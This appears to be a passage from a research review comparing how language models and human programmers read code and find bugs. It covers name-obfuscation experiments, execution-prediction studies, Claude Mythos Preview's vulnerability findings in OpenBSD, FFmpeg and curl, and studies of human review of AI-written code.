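Granberry and colleagues find this encouraging, and they are right when the goal is to find bugs. An automatic checker can test `all_paid` against the specification "returns True only if every invoice is paid", and the code will fail. But if a reviewer asks what the function does and the model replies with the same sentence, it has presented the intended behaviour as the actual behaviour, so the answer is false and hides the bug.

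Eight programs and one model from early 2024 can't show how often this happens, but they do show that a model can help find a bug by reading for intent, which is the opposite of what the hypothesis proposes.

### Changing the names

Shen and colleagues built Face/Off, a testing framework that varies the names used in a program. The program can keep its informative names, receive anonymous placeholders such as `func0` and `var1`, or receive misleading names taken from an unrelated program. A milder condition uses similar words. The table shows the results for GPT-4o-mini.

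| Task | Original names | Anonymous names | Misleading names |
|---|---|---|---|
| Decide whether a description fits the code | 88.3% | 79.7% | 67.9% |
| Choose which of two descriptions fits | 99.0% | 99.0% | 76.1% |
| Complete a half-written function | 88.2% | 83.9% | 73.2% |
| Work out the type of one variable | 82.6% | 79.5% | 84.9% |

Names carry information about the purpose of code, so a reader will find it harder to match code to a description without them. A lower score with anonymous names therefore isn't necessarily a fault in the model.

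A more revealing test had models choose between the correct description and one of the program that had supplied the misleading names. GPT-4o-mini did no worse with anonymous names, so it could evidently find the right answer without the original names. But with misleading names, it chose the wrong description in almost a quarter of cases. Llama 3 70B's accuracy similarly fell from 98.6% to 73.3%, and GPT-3.5's fell to 52.4%, barely better than chance.

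In an example from Shen and colleagues' completion task, the original function calculates how far the numbers in a list typically lie from their average. When its names were changed to suggest counting odd and even numbers, GPT-3.5 completed it with code that did so, although the existing lines were calculating an average. Function names seem to matter most, since replacing only the function's name harmed summaries more than replacing one parameter or one local variable.

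Names have much less influence when the surrounding code makes a variable's type (a number, say, or a piece of text) clear, as the last row of the table shows. Shen and colleagues chose 317 such variables and renamed only those. Across three models, the scores changed by about three percentage points at most and in no consistent direction.

The researchers warned the models that names might have changed, and in some tests had them replace the names with placeholders before answering. This recovered only some of the lost accuracy on summaries. All the models in Face/Off are old by now, and none is a reasoning model, so the experiment is better evidence of how training on code can affect a model's reading than of how current reviewers behave.

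Le, Pham and colleagues (2025), in *When Names Disappear*, tested somewhat stronger models. They first asked the models to summarize code and had GPT-4o score the summaries, including its own. When the researchers removed descriptive names from classes (bundles of related functions), GPT-4o's score fell from 87.3 to 58.7 and DeepSeek V3's fell from 87.7 to 76.7. One class implements the game Minesweeper. GPT-4o recognized the game when the names were present, but gave a line-by-line description of updates to a grid when they were removed.

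That line-by-line account is a literal reading, accurate but of little use to somebody who wants to know what the program is for. GPT-4o's score fell much less on summaries of contest solutions, from 73.4 to 70.1. Contest programmers use names like `a` and `n` anyway, and the purpose of an algorithm is usually clear from its structure.

Execution prediction is a fairer test of literal reading. Le and colleagues used it on 96 of the more complex contest solutions, comparing the original names with placeholders, strings of characters that are hard to tell apart, and names that suggest the wrong behaviour.

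| Model | Original | Placeholders | Hard to tell apart | Misleading |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 82.9% | 75.5% | 68.7% | 82.3% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 80.2% | 65.3% | 56.4% | 75.5% |
| Qwen3-Coder 480B | 99.3% | 94.5% | 88.4% | 93.8% |
| DeepSeek V3 | 99.3% | 98.6% | 91.8% | 97.2% |

All four models lost accuracy, so none was reading the code perfectly literally. If they had been following the program's apparent purpose, misleading names should have hurt them most, but hard-to-distinguish names hurt every model more. The most likely explanation is that the models lost track of which variable was which, as people probably would too. Misleading names did more harm in a second set of programs with richer names, where they lowered Qwen3-Coder's accuracy by almost nine points. That set contained only 37 programs, though, so three or four of them could account for the whole difference.

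Names can also lead a model to repeat an answer it has already seen. Le and colleagues gave the programs new inputs and counted how often a model replied with the output for the old input. GPT-4o did this 13 times on the contest programs with their original names, 5 times with the hard-to-distinguish names and twice with the misleading ones. DeepSeek V3 never did it on those programs. Such recall inflates scores on published tests, but it shouldn't matter much for a company's private code, which the model is unlikely to have seen.

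### Looking for a bug in edited code

In each prompt, Haroon and colleagues described what a program should do, told the model that the program's output was incorrect, and asked which line was responsible. They changed the code's appearance but kept the specification fixed, so a model that read the code literally should have found the same bug every time.

All nine models fell far short of this, including Claude 3.7 Sonnet, one of the strongest. The figures below are averages for bugs that a model had already located in the unedited program.

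| Edit that leaves behaviour unchanged | Share of bugs located again |
|---|---|
| Misleading variable names | 28.7% |
| Misleading comments | 24.6% |
| Added code that has no effect | 18.5% |
| All three together | 15.8% |

Some of these losses would probably have happened without any edits. The models often had low success rates to begin with, and a model that found a bug partly by luck may miss it on a second attempt. The differences between rows are therefore more informative than the size of the loss in any one row.

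Changing the order of functions in Java programs cut accuracy by 83%, even though it adds nothing misleading. Half of the bugs that the models located were in the first quarter of the program, and only 18% were in the last quarter. These programs averaged about 250 lines, far more than the functions in most execution-prediction tests. The results fit the part of the prediction that says models' errors come from length and complexity. They don't fit the idea that models succeed by reading literally, because a literal reader would ignore code that never runs.

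Comments influence models for the same reason as names. They are part of the same input as the code and usually agree with it, so training encourages the model to rely on them. Pull request descriptions probably work in a similar way. An accurate description gives the model an intent to compare the code with, which it badly needs, but an inaccurate one can supply the wrong intent or lead the model to assume that the code already works as described. None of these experiments varied pull request descriptions, so the size of their effect is unknown.

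### Two recent models with opposite results

The newest models tested in these experiments are GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3, both from late 2025, and stronger ones have come out since. *How Robustly do LLMs Understand Execution Semantics?* (Spiess, Devanbu and Barr, 2026) and *Are Large Language Models Robust in Understanding Code Against Semantics-Preserving Mutations?* (Orvalho and Kwiatkowska, 2025) both tested these two models on CRUXEval, a set of 800 short Python functions. Both teams renamed variables and asked the models for the program's output.

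| Model | Spiess and colleagues: original | Renamed | Orvalho and Kwiatkowska: original | Renamed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 99.2% | 75.8% | 86.0% | 87.0% |
| Gemini 3 | 99.2% | 98.4% | 76.8% | 66.2% |

Renaming badly hurts GPT-5.2's performance and barely affects Gemini 3's in one experiment, but in the other it hurts Gemini 3's and doesn't affect GPT-5.2's. Sensitivity to names evidently depends on how the researchers pose the question and isn't a fixed property of either model.

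Spiess and colleagues left the models on their default settings and told them to give only the answer. Orvalho and Kwiatkowska also asked for an explanation, told most models when an answer was wrong, and let them try again. They created up to two renamed versions of each program. If they counted a program as correct when a model got either version right, the extra chance could explain why most of their models scored higher after renaming.

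GPT-5.2 may have done little reasoning before it answered in the first experiment. Spiess and colleagues don't test this, but one of their results is consistent with it. GPT-5.2's accuracy fell from 99.1% to 79.6% when they changed the inputs but not the programs or their names, so misleading names can't explain the drop. The model might have learned the published answers, or it might have estimated outputs instead of working them out. It got all the new inputs right for only 56% of programs, compared with 97% for Gemini 3 Pro. GPT-5 Nano, a smaller and older model, did so for 83%, so general ability doesn't explain GPT-5.2's low score.

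Reasoning that a model writes after its answer can explain or contradict the answer but can't improve it. In one example from Orvalho and Kwiatkowska's paper, a program returns the largest product of any selection from the numbers −4, −5 and −4. GPT-5.2 answered 80 before listing the selections and their products, none of which equals 80. On its second attempt it gave the correct answer, 20.

Orvalho and Kwiatkowska also report large losses after changes to a program's structure. When they unrolled loops by moving the last one or two iterations out and writing them separately, Gemini 3's score on contest programs fell from 100% to 29.6%. I would not read much into this figure, because all nine models kept between about 24% and 33% of their original scores, even though those scores ranged from 33% to 100%. The losses may be so similar because the edit applied to only about three programs in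 ten and the rest counted as failures.

Their check of the models' reasoning is more useful. Experts read the explanation for every correct answer on the contest programs and judged whether it described what the program actually did. For Llama 3.2, a small model, 55% of correct answers rested on flawed reasoning, compared with 0.2% for both GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3. This suggests that strong models trace short programs when they explain their answers, although both models may have seen these programs in training.

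However, the experts may have judged the reasoning too generously. One response published as an example of sound reasoning comes from GraniteCode, a small model that was asked whether "a" is the acronym of "an" and "apple". It first answered True. When told this was wrong, it answered False, the only other possibility, and explained that the first letters of the two words are "an", when they are "a" and "a".

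### Running the code

A coding agent can run `all_paid` instead of predicting what it returns. If it calls the function with one paid and one unpaid invoice, it will see that the result is True. The names don't affect the result, so the agent has established the behaviour for that input without reading the loop. Execution-prediction tests don't let the agent run the code, so they measure a skill it may not always need.

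But running a program shows only what happens for the inputs someone tries. An agent that infers the function's purpose from its name may try only an all-paid list and an all-unpaid one, and neither exposes the bug. Intended reading then affects which tests the agent chooses instead of what results it predicts.

Tools can choose inputs more systematically. PathCrawler, which Granberry and colleagues used, tries to make a program follow each of its possible paths. In the invoice function, one path handles an unpaid invoice and then a paid one. The function returns True, which is wrong for `all_paid`, but PathCrawler can't detect the error because it has no record of what the function is for. Someone still has to supply the right answer. If an agent copies the observed output into a new test, that test will pass only while the bug remains.

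When Granberry and colleagues added PathCrawler's inputs and outputs to the prompt, GPT-4 wrote more about the code's purpose in its specifications. In one case PathCrawler supplied only two examples, and GPT-4 treated a coincidence in them as a rule, writing a specification that required both inputs to be 0 or 1.

Reading code can also establish things that running it can't. Anyone who follows the loop in `all_paid` can see that it returns True for every list containing a paid invoice, whereas tests can only sample those lists. Some code is also awkward or dangerous to run, because it charges a customer's card, deletes records or depends on equipment that the agent doesn't have. A sensible agent will read the code to decide what to run, then use the results to correct its reading.

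### An ability that models don't always use

Changing the names in a program changed the answers of models from 2023 and 2024, contrary to the prediction that names make no difference. These models treated altered programs as the familiar originals, and misleading names led them towards the wrong description. The prediction is roughly right for reasoning models working out the output of a short program. o3-mini made almost no errors on altered programs, and in tests by Spiess and colleagues, renaming lowered Gemini 3 Pro's score by less than one percentage point.

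Some evidence also supports the idea that the remaining errors come from length and complexity. Across the 14 models that Spiess and colleagues tested, accuracy was 59% when a run involved at most one decision, such as whether to repeat a loop, and 34% when it involved more than 27. Most of those models were small, and Gemini 3 Pro showed no such decline. The models of late 2026 are unlikely to be worse at this, but none of these experiments tested them.

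Whether a model can trace code is less in doubt than whether it does so during a review. A model asked for the code's output on a particular input has one right answer to find, but a model asked to review a change is given no input and has to decide which parts to trace and for which cases.

Spiess and colleagues gave models inputs that make a program stop with an error, using a prompt that didn't mention errors. GPT-5.2 predicted the right error only 15% of the time. Adding an instruction and an example saying that the code might raise an error increased its accuracy to 81%, and Gemini 3 Pro's from 49% to 98%. The models were already able to predict errors, but the first prompt implied that the program would produce a value, and they often supplied one. The smaller models in Marinov and colleagues' study showed a similar bias, since their most common mistake on the short human-written programs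 was to say that a faulty program would run successfully.

A prompt that mentioned errors and told the model to keep track of types also lowered GPT-5.2's accuracy on programs that ran normally, from 81% to 76%, partly because the model now predicted errors that didn't occur.

How literally a model reads code depends partly on what it expects the answer to look like, and a reviewer's instructions help set that expectation. To show that models catch bugs because they read literally, researchers would need to vary the names in the code under real review, keep the specification fixed, and check whether current models still report the same bugs. Haroon and colleagues came closest to this, and the models they tested often failed.

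## What people and models each find in the same code

To find out whether people and models miss different bugs, researchers have to give both the same code. Few have done so, and those few tested students and mostly weak models. Security teams have since used a much stronger model to search software that professionals had reviewed for decades, but nobody gave people the same task under the same conditions.

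### Twenty functions for students and small models

Obfuscation means rewriting a program so that it is harder to read but behaves the same. Nguyen, Le and colleagues (2026), in *The Effect of Code Obfuscation on Human Program Comprehension*, used it to make five versions of each of 20 short functions, ten in Python and ten in JavaScript. One version kept the original variable names. The others had meaningless names, misleading names borrowed from unrelated code, a scrambled structure that hides the order of the steps, or both a scrambled structure and meaningless names. Fifty computer science undergraduates then each predicted the output of 12 functions with pencil and paper, unable to run the code.

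Le, Nguyen and Nguyen (2026), in *Do Machines Struggle Where Humans Do?*, gave the same programs to seven small language models. The table shows how often the students and the two strongest models were right.

| Version | All students | Students with over a year's experience | DeepSeek-R1-Distill 7B | SmolLM3 3B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Original variable names | 40.5% | 40.5% | 63.8% | 45.0% |
| Meaningless names | 38.7% | 44.0% | 64.2% | 44.0% |
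| Misleading names | 38.0% | 55.6% | 51.8% | 34.2% |
| Scrambled structure | 34.2% | 40.0% | 57.0% | 37.6% |
| Scrambled structure, meaningless names | 31.1% | 37.5% | 56.2% | 33.0% |

Misleading names hurt the models more than the students. The students lost 2.4 percentage points, while the two models lost 11 to 12. This is almost the opposite of what we would expect if people read for intent and models read literally. The models evidently didn't need the original names, because they did just as well with meaningless ones. The wrong names hurt them, as in the Face/Off experiments with older models.

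However, the effect on students differed by language. Misleading names cut their accuracy on JavaScript from 43.3% to 26.2% but raised it on Python from 37.5% to 50.0%. Each figure comes from only about 60 answers. The fall in JavaScript is barely large enough to rule out chance, and the rise in Python is not large enough. Nguyen and colleagues suggest that the original Python names encouraged wrong guesses. For example, one function splits a sentence into a list of words, and students who saw the original names tended to give the right words but forget that the answer should be a list. This explanation may be right, but they thought of it after seeing the results.

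The "original" programs used as the baseline also lacked their most informative name, because the researchers called every function `myFunct` except in the misleading version. The students might have relied on function names more if the experiment had kept the real ones.

The answer times are better evidence that people trust names. When names were misleading, correct answers took longer than wrong ones in both languages, while in most other versions correct answers tended to be faster. This fits the idea that hurried readers believed the names while patient ones checked the code. But nobody told the students how long to take, so the more careful ones may also have been better programmers.

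Many students probably didn't trace the code. One function computes a sequence in which each number is the sum of the three before it, and returns 927 for the input 14. Of the twelve students who saw it with original or misleading names, one gave the right answer. Most of the others gave a number close to the input, such as 12 or 15, or a small number from the Fibonacci sequence, in which each number is the sum of the two before it.

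Le, Nguyen and Nguyen emphasize that the more experienced students' accuracy rose from 40.5% to 55.6% when the names were misleading. They take this as a sign that experts rely on structure instead of names, and they point out that no model improved in the same way. But these experts were undergraduates with more than a year's experience of the language, and the percentages correspond to 17 correct answers out of 42 and 15 out of 27. A gap that wide would appear by chance about one time in five even if names made no difference.

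The model results also have weaknesses. The largest of the seven models has only eight billion parameters, and five of the seven got less than a quarter of the answers right on every version. Le, Nguyen and Nguyen also averaged the results over 21 prompts, some of which left the models very little room to reason. Each model produced 500 answers per version, but all for the same 20 functions, so the large number of runs provides little evidence of how the models would do on other code. Current reasoning models solve functions this short almost every time, at least when the functions are accurately named.

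The result most relevant to the third prediction compares which programs the students and the models found hard. Le, Nguyen and Nguyen ranked the programs by how often the students got them right, did the same for each model, and measured how well each model's ranking agreed with the students', where 1 means perfect agreement and 0 means none. Agreement was between 0.30 and 0.47 for the four reasoning models and between 0.02 and 0.10 for the other three. Phi-4 Mini had the highest agreement, but it answered only about 4% of the questions correctly, so its ranking depends on few correct answers. Agreement for the strongest model was 0.37.

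So the models that reason before answering, as most AI reviewers now do, tended to fail where the students failed. This counts against the third prediction, though not decisively, because a convoluted function is hard for anyone and two readers can get it wrong for different reasons. Models also seem to have difficulties of their own. *Beyond Accuracy* (Mächtle, Serr and colleagues, 2026) tested whether models could tell if a given output matched a program and its input, and found that the usual measures of how complex code is for people only partly explained the results.

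### Surprised by the same code

Abdelsalam and colleagues compared recordings from 24 programmers of the brain signal that follows a glance at confusing code with the perplexity of a model, Qwen2.5-Coder-32B, on the same snippets. Perplexity measures how poorly a model predicts a piece of text. A token that the model gives a one-in-four chance of coming next has a perplexity of 4, and one that it gives a one-in-a-hundred chance has a perplexity of 100.

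The snippets contained atoms of confusion, small patterns that people often misread. In one example, the confusing version decreases a variable in the middle of a longer expression, and the plain version does this on a separate line. The highest perplexity was 555 in the confusing version and 1 in the plain one. Across all the confusing fragments, the correlation between the highest perplexity and the strength of the brain signal was 0.47. For the plain fragments it was 0.05, indistinguishable from zero. Abdelsalam and colleagues also looked for peaks in perplexity without using the list of known patterns, and the peaks they found overlapped with 46 of the 72 confusing fragments.

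A model that flags unlikely text will often flag code that people already find confusing. This is useful, but it doesn't help them catch the ordinary-looking bugs they miss.

The comparison doesn't measure whether people or models would get the answer right. Perplexity depends on the probability a model assigns to a token given the text before it, and a model can assign `V1--` a low probability and still work out its effect correctly. The snippets were also all correct programs, and the 0.47 is a rough figure because each snippet had at most 12 usable recordings.

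### Students who missed bugs and models that found too many

In an older experiment, reported in *Decoding Logic Errors* (2023), MacNeil, Leinonen and colleagues asked 964 students on a first-year programming course, as well as GPT-3 and GPT-4, to look for bugs rather than predict outputs. They used three short C functions, each with one correct version and three faulty ones.

| Reviewer | Named the bug in faulty code | Passed correct code |
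|---|---|---|
| Students | 34.5% | 92.8% |
| GPT-3 | 87.3% | 79.4% |
| GPT-4 | 99.2% | 42.2% |

GPT-4 missed almost no bugs, but it also reported problems in more than half of the correct functions, often over trivial matters such as naming conventions. If half the functions in a batch were faulty, GPT-3 would judge 83% of them correctly, GPT-4 71% and the students 64%. The scoring favored the models because a response to faulty code counted as correct if it named the real bug, no matter how many nonexistent bugs it also listed. GPT-4 reported about 1.7 more bugs per function than the students.

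The students had to describe each function's purpose and then list any errors in light of that description, which practically instructed them to read for intent, as the hypothesis says human readers do. But every group wrote the description, so we can't tell whether it helped or hurt them. The students were also beginners, and many will have missed an error because they didn't know enough C.

One of the supposedly correct functions shows how hard it is to count false alarms. `AverageNegativeValues` adds up the negative numbers in an array and divides by how many there are. If there are none, it divides by zero. MacNeil and colleagues accepted only "no bugs" or a blank response for this version, so they would have marked a reviewer wrong for raising the problem. As with the empty list of invoices, it is unclear from the code alone whether this is a bug.

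### Bugs that survived decades of review

By 2026, models were finding bugs in software that experts had examined for years. In April, Anthropic gave selected organizations access to Claude Mythos Preview, a general-purpose model that turned out to be unusually good at finding security flaws. *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes a 27-year-old bug that the model found in OpenBSD, an operating system known mainly for its security.

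The bug is in OpenBSD code that tracks data arriving over a network. Each byte has a position number, and the code keeps a list of gaps, the stretches that haven't arrived yet. One passage is dangerous only if a certain position comes both before a gap and after everything received so far. This looks as impossible as a number being both less than 5 and greater than 10.

But the position numbers wrap round at their maximum, like the hours on a clock. To decide which of two positions comes first, the code subtracts one from the other and checks the sign. This works as long as the two are fairly close together, which they always are in normal traffic. An earlier check was supposed to reject anything out of range, but it tested only one end of the range. The comparison can then give contradictory answers, in which case the supposedly impossible condition is met and the machine crashes.

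This bug fits the hypothesis better than any other in this section. A reader who takes the comparison to mean "is this position earlier?" has read its intended meaning, and will conclude that the dangerous code can never run. To see the bug, the reader has to work out what the subtraction does with numbers nobody expected it to receive, and connect that to a missing check elsewhere.

A 16-year-old bug in FFmpeg, a widely used video library, is similar. FFmpeg divides each frame of a video into slices and records which slice each part of the picture belongs to. It first fills this record with −1, meaning "no slice yet", but the entries can't hold negative numbers, so the −1 becomes 65,535, which is also a possible slice number. Real videos use only a handful of slices per frame, so they never reach that number. A programmer who sees the −1 will naturally read it as "none" and look no further.

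According to Carlini and colleagues, every reviewer missed this bug, and so did fuzzing, which tests a program by feeding it millions of randomly generated files. Nobody recorded what the reviewers were thinking. Some may have taken the −1 at face value, and others may have skimmed the file or never opened it.

The model, too, combined reading with testing. Carlini and colleagues gave it a copy of the program and a short request to find a vulnerability. In a typical run, it read the code, guessed where a flaw might be, and ran the program to test the guess, adding logging where that helped. This resembles the cycle of hypothesis and checking that Brooks described in people, except that the model's hypotheses were about what could go wrong and it could check them by running the program.

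The published examples are also mostly memory errors, in which a program reads or writes memory that it shouldn't. Carlini and colleagues concentrated on these partly because an automatic tool can confirm them. Recognizing such errors doesn't require a specification, so a model could be very good at finding them and still miss the bug in `all_paid`.

Mozilla, which makes the Firefox browser, fixed 271 vulnerabilities that Mythos Preview had found in one release. LWN's *Firefox* (2026) quotes Mozilla's announcement that the model could find every category of vulnerability that people can. A reader quotes another passage, in which Mozilla says it saw no bug that an elite human researcher couldn't have found. If so, the model and the best human researchers differ more in how many bugs they find than in what kind.

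In the comments on the LWN article, another reader, farnz, suggests that models are good at noticing code that no person could plausibly have meant to write. That would make them good at intended reading, which is the reverse of the hypothesis. This is only a comment, but the OpenBSD and FFmpeg bugs are compatible with it. In FFmpeg, for example, nobody would intend the value that means "no slice" to also be the number of a slice.

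### How many of the findings were real

Unlike GPT-4, which tended to object to everything, the model has mostly been right when people checked its reports of serious bugs. Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) states that by 22 May the model had reported 23,019 possible vulnerabilities in more than 1,000 open-source projects and rated 6,202 of them as high or critical in severity. Security researchers, nearly all from six independent firms, had checked 1,752 of those 6,202 and found that 1,587 (90.6%) were real and 1,094 (62.4%) deserved a high or critical rating. Cloudflare, which used the model on its own systems, considered the model's rate of false alarms better than that of human testers.

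Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked*, published later in 2026, reports that people outside Anthropic had reviewed only 1,900 of the 23,019 findings across all levels of severity by the same date. The reviewed findings were probably not a random sample. If the most convincing reports went out first, the remaining 21,119 will contain a larger share of mistakes.

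The model's severity ratings were less reliable than its findings. Help Net Security compares its ratings with later ones by maintainers and independent scorers for 27 vulnerabilities with an official public identifier. The model overstated the severity of 13 and understated that of one. It rated eight as critical, and only one of those kept that rating. For example, it gave the top rating to a flaw in Temporal Server, a tool for running long business processes, but Temporal's maintainers rated it low because an attacker would already need a privileged internal password.

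Carlini and colleagues had reported much better agreement, with expert contractors giving exactly the same rating as the model in 89% of 198 cases. The two samples differ, and the judges also had different knowledge. A contractor who reads a bug report can confirm what the code allows, but the maintainers know how people install the software and who holds which passwords, little of which is in the code. The model may have described the behaviour accurately but misjudged its importance because it didn't know how people were meant to use the program.

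By 22 May, maintainers had patched only 75 of the 530 serious bugs that Anthropic had reported to them. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Project Glasswing Update*, finds this suspicious and objects that Anthropic won't release the details. Anthropic replies in effect that most of the reports were recent, that volunteers are overloaded, and that publishing an unpatched flaw would put users at risk. The low number of patches is better evidence of the maintainers' workload than of whether the bugs exist. The secrecy is a more serious problem for anyone comparing people with models, because outsiders can't examine the bugs to see why people missed them.

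Curl, a tool for transferring data, runs on billions of devices, and its developers already test and audit it heavily. In *Mythos finds a curl vulnerability*, its lead developer, Daniel Stenberg (2026), describes a report from someone who had used the AI model Mythos to analyse 178,000 lines of curl's code. The report listed five "confirmed" vulnerabilities. After several hours' work, curl's security team accepted one, of low severity. Another was an ordinary bug, and the other three were shortcomings that curl's documentation already told users to expect.

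The report also described about twenty bugs that weren't security problems, with hardly any false alarms. Even so, Stenberg concluded that the excitement about the model was mainly marketing. Other AI tools had already led to 200 to 300 fixes in curl over the previous eight to ten months, including probably a dozen or more published vulnerabilities. Stenberg acknowledges that those tools had easier bugs to find, so the counts can't be used to tell which tool is best.

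Stenberg is much more positive about AI reviewers in general, which he finds far better than older automatic tools. Unlike those tools, he says, they can detect when code contradicts the comment beside it. They can also use information about the network protocols that curl implements, and about how third-party libraries behave, to detect when curl relies on a false assumption. In each case the model goes beyond literal reading by comparing the code with some record of what it should do.

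### Repairing the Logic Theorist

*Executable Archaeology* (Shrager, 2026) describes a small project in which people, models and a conventional tool each found faults that the others hadn't. Shrager wanted to run the Logic Theorist, a 1950s program that proves theorems in logic and that many regard as the first AI. He worked from a version of its code printed in a 1963 report. The code is in IPL-V, a language that fell out of use in the 1960s, so he had to write an interpreter, a program that carries out IPL-V instructions on a modern computer.

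Shrager and a colleague copied the code from the report by hand. Several people checked the copy repeatedly but missed a surprising number of small errors. A tool called gridlock, which extracts tables of code from scanned documents and isn't a language model, eventually caught several. The reviewers were comparing two texts and didn't need to understand either, so reading for intent probably doesn't fully explain the missed errors. Checking page after page of obscure symbols is also tiring. Nobody asked a model to do the same checking, so the episode doesn't show that a model would have done better.

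The project began using models later, when the program ran without crashing but failed to prove simple theorems. The Logic Theorist works by trying things and backing out of dead ends, which made it very hard to tell a bug from a normal failed attempt. Shrager could no longer follow the program over thousands of lines of output. Google's Gemini found one fault in the interpreter after several hours of work over several days. Claude then traced another to J74, the operation that copies a list.

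At that point Shrager and Claude were stuck, because both had read Shrager's version of J74 and the manual's specification and saw no difference between them. Shrager guessed what was wrong, and Claude compared the code with an original version of J74, transcribed from 1962 punched cards. The two versions differed just as Shrager had guessed, and changing one line fixed the program. Without the cards, literal reading could not have found the mismatch, because the manual was too vague.

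The models had learned IPL-V largely from Shrager's interpreter, so they sometimes repeated its errors in their suggestions. They also sometimes made the mistake of trying to correct the Logic Theorist instead of the interpreter. Shrager credits them above all with "tenacity", since they would read thousands of lines of output and insert checks in hundreds of places.

### Patience, repetition, money and knowledge

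Tenacity could also explain much of what Mythos Preview found. The source code of curl contains about 660,000 words, more than *War and Peace*, and no person can give every line the same attention. A model can examine the last file as closely as the first. But tenacity is hard to separate from literal reading, because tracing code takes time. The students who were right despite misleading names were also slower. A person with enough time and a reason to use it might read as literally as any model.

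Repetition matters as well. Suppose that a single run of a model has a probability *p* of finding a particular bug and that the runs are independent. The chance that at least one of *n* runs finds it is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

If a model has a 1% chance of finding a bug in each run, a hundred independent runs will find it at least once 63% of the time. A person with a 20% chance of finding it in one reading looks worse than that, although one reading is twenty times as likely to find the bug as one run. Real runs aren't independent, because a model tends to repeat its mistakes, so the gain from repetition is smaller.

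Carlini and colleagues ran the model about a thousand times on OpenBSD. They directed different runs to different files, so we can't conclude that the model needed a thousand attempts to find the 27-year-old bug. We also don't know in how many runs the model read the faulty code and missed the bug.

Those thousand runs cost less than $20,000 and produced several dozen other findings. Nobody has spent the same amount on human experts to see what they would find. At $200 an hour, $20,000 would pay for 100 hours of work. Mozilla's remark about elite researchers suggests they could have found any one of these bugs, but there are few such people and an enormous amount of code.

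A difference in knowledge explains some findings well and others poorly. A curl developer may never have read an obscure clause in a protocol that a model has effectively memorized. But the programmers who wrote OpenBSD's comparison certainly knew that position numbers wrap round, because they designed the comparison to handle it. FFmpeg's developers presumably knew how a computer stores −1. In those two cases people had the facts but didn't put them together, more likely because they paid too little attention or relied too much on what the code was meant to do.

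The way these examples came to light can also mislead. A bug that has lasted 27 years is one that people missed, so a list of old bugs found by a model will always make the model look good and the people look bad. Nobody has compiled the matching list of bugs that people found after the model had missed them, but it would have some entries. While Stenberg was still writing about the curl scan, security researchers, many of whom use AI themselves, sent in more reports of suspected problems.

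### Different misses, but perhaps not because of names

The third prediction is right to the extent that people and models don't miss exactly the same bugs. Mythos Preview found more than a thousand serious flaws that the software's developers had overlooked, and outside experts confirmed them. A team that adds such a model to its human reviewers will very probably catch more bugs.

There is much less support for the claim that people and models tend to make mistakes on different code. In the one experiment that compared them program by program, the reasoning models had trouble with many of the same functions as the students. The brain recordings also suggest overlap, since a model and a group of programmers reacted to the same fragments. Both results come from short snippets and models well below the current best, so they may not hold for a strong model reviewing a large program.

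The idea that people and models find different things because they read code differently has even less support. If that were the cause, misleading names should have hurt the students much more than the models, and they didn't. The OpenBSD bug looks like a case of people reading for intent, but patience and repetition explain most of the field results at least as well.

The searches of real software can't measure the error correlation, however many bugs they find. That would require knowing which bugs the people and the model both missed, and those bugs remain undiscovered.

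## How people review code that an AI wrote

When a coding agent writes a change, the names, comments, tests and description all come from one interpretation of a prompt that the reviewer may never see. A colleague writing the same change would know the project and could answer the reviewer's questions.

### One misunderstanding, repeated everywhere

Suppose a shop asks an agent to ship each order "once the customer has paid". The shop means that every invoice must be paid, but the agent writes this:

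```python
def has_paid(invoices):
    """Return True if the customer has paid an invoice."""
    return any(invoice.paid for invoice in invoices)
```

The agent also writes a test that expects True when one invoice is paid and one isn't. It describes the pull request as "Ships orders after payment", and all the tests pass.

In the earlier function `all_paid`, the name contradicted the loop, so a reader who traced the loop could find the bug. Tracing `has_paid` only confirms the comment, because all the beacons point to the same purpose and the code fulfils it. To find the bug, the reviewer needs to know what the shop wanted, and even the prompt is ambiguous about that.

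A human programmer could make the same mistake and write equally consistent tests. But they might remember that large orders have two invoices, and a reviewer could ask them what "paid" was supposed to mean. *Plausible Is Not Enough* (Rahman, Alam and colleagues, 2026) quotes a reviewer who said that with AI-generated code "there's no author intent to appeal to".

### Spinellis's argument

The software engineering researcher Diomidis Spinellis argues that people need to understand a system better when they work with AI than without it. In *Why reviewing AI-generated code is devilishly hard* (Spinellis, 2026), he describes ordinary programming as having a "built-in control gate". Programmers who don't understand the code usually can't make a working change to it, so they discover their lack of understanding. Someone reviewing an AI-written change that has already passed its automated tests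 gets no such warning, and may approve it in the mistaken belief that they understand it.

People reviewing a colleague's code don't get that warning either, but the colleague does, so at least one person probably understands the change. When an agent writes the code, nobody may understand it.

Spinellis adds that people judge their own understanding badly. In a well-known psychology experiment, students greatly overestimated how well they understood devices such as sewing machines and can openers. He suspects the same is true of algorithms and software designs, and that junior programmers are most at risk.

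He also thinks the code itself is misleading. People make mistakes for many reasons, such as forgetting a step or misapplying a rule, and a reviewer who thinks differently from the author has a good chance of noticing them. A model builds code from probable tokens, so its faulty code tends to look right. If so, looking for improbable code, which helps find human bugs, should work less well on a model's code.

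People are prone to automation bias, which means trusting an automated system too much and checking its work too little. They may accept a wrong suggestion or overlook something the system failed to do, such as write a test.

Most of this is extrapolated from psychology and other kinds of automation. But researchers can test the claim about automation bias by measuring whether people check the same code less carefully when they believe an AI wrote it.

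### Telling reviewers that an AI wrote the code

Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026), in *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, tracked the eyes of 32 software practitioners from 20 organizations as they reviewed four Python files of about 77 lines each. People had written all the code, but the researchers labelled some passages as the work of an invented AI tool. They rotated the labels so that each passage was labelled for only some participants.

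Participants looked at the labelled passages for longer. They spent about five extra seconds on a six-line passage that took 15 seconds on average, and about 15 extra seconds (60% more) on a more complex 25-line passage. The label made little difference on very short passages.

The length of the reviewers' eye movements didn't change. People who are reading closely tend to make shorter eye movements, so Khojah and colleagues conclude that the label made reviewers slower but no more thorough. This is a weak measure of thoroughness, since someone who traces a loop three times may make eye movements of the same length as someone who traces it once. The researchers also cite earlier work in which people who looked at buggy code for longer tended to find more bugs. They planted faults in all four files but didn't assess whether participants found them, so we don't know whether the extra time helped.

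The label may also have attracted attention for reasons unrelated to trust. It came with highlighting and the prompt that had supposedly produced the code, both of which gave people more to look at.

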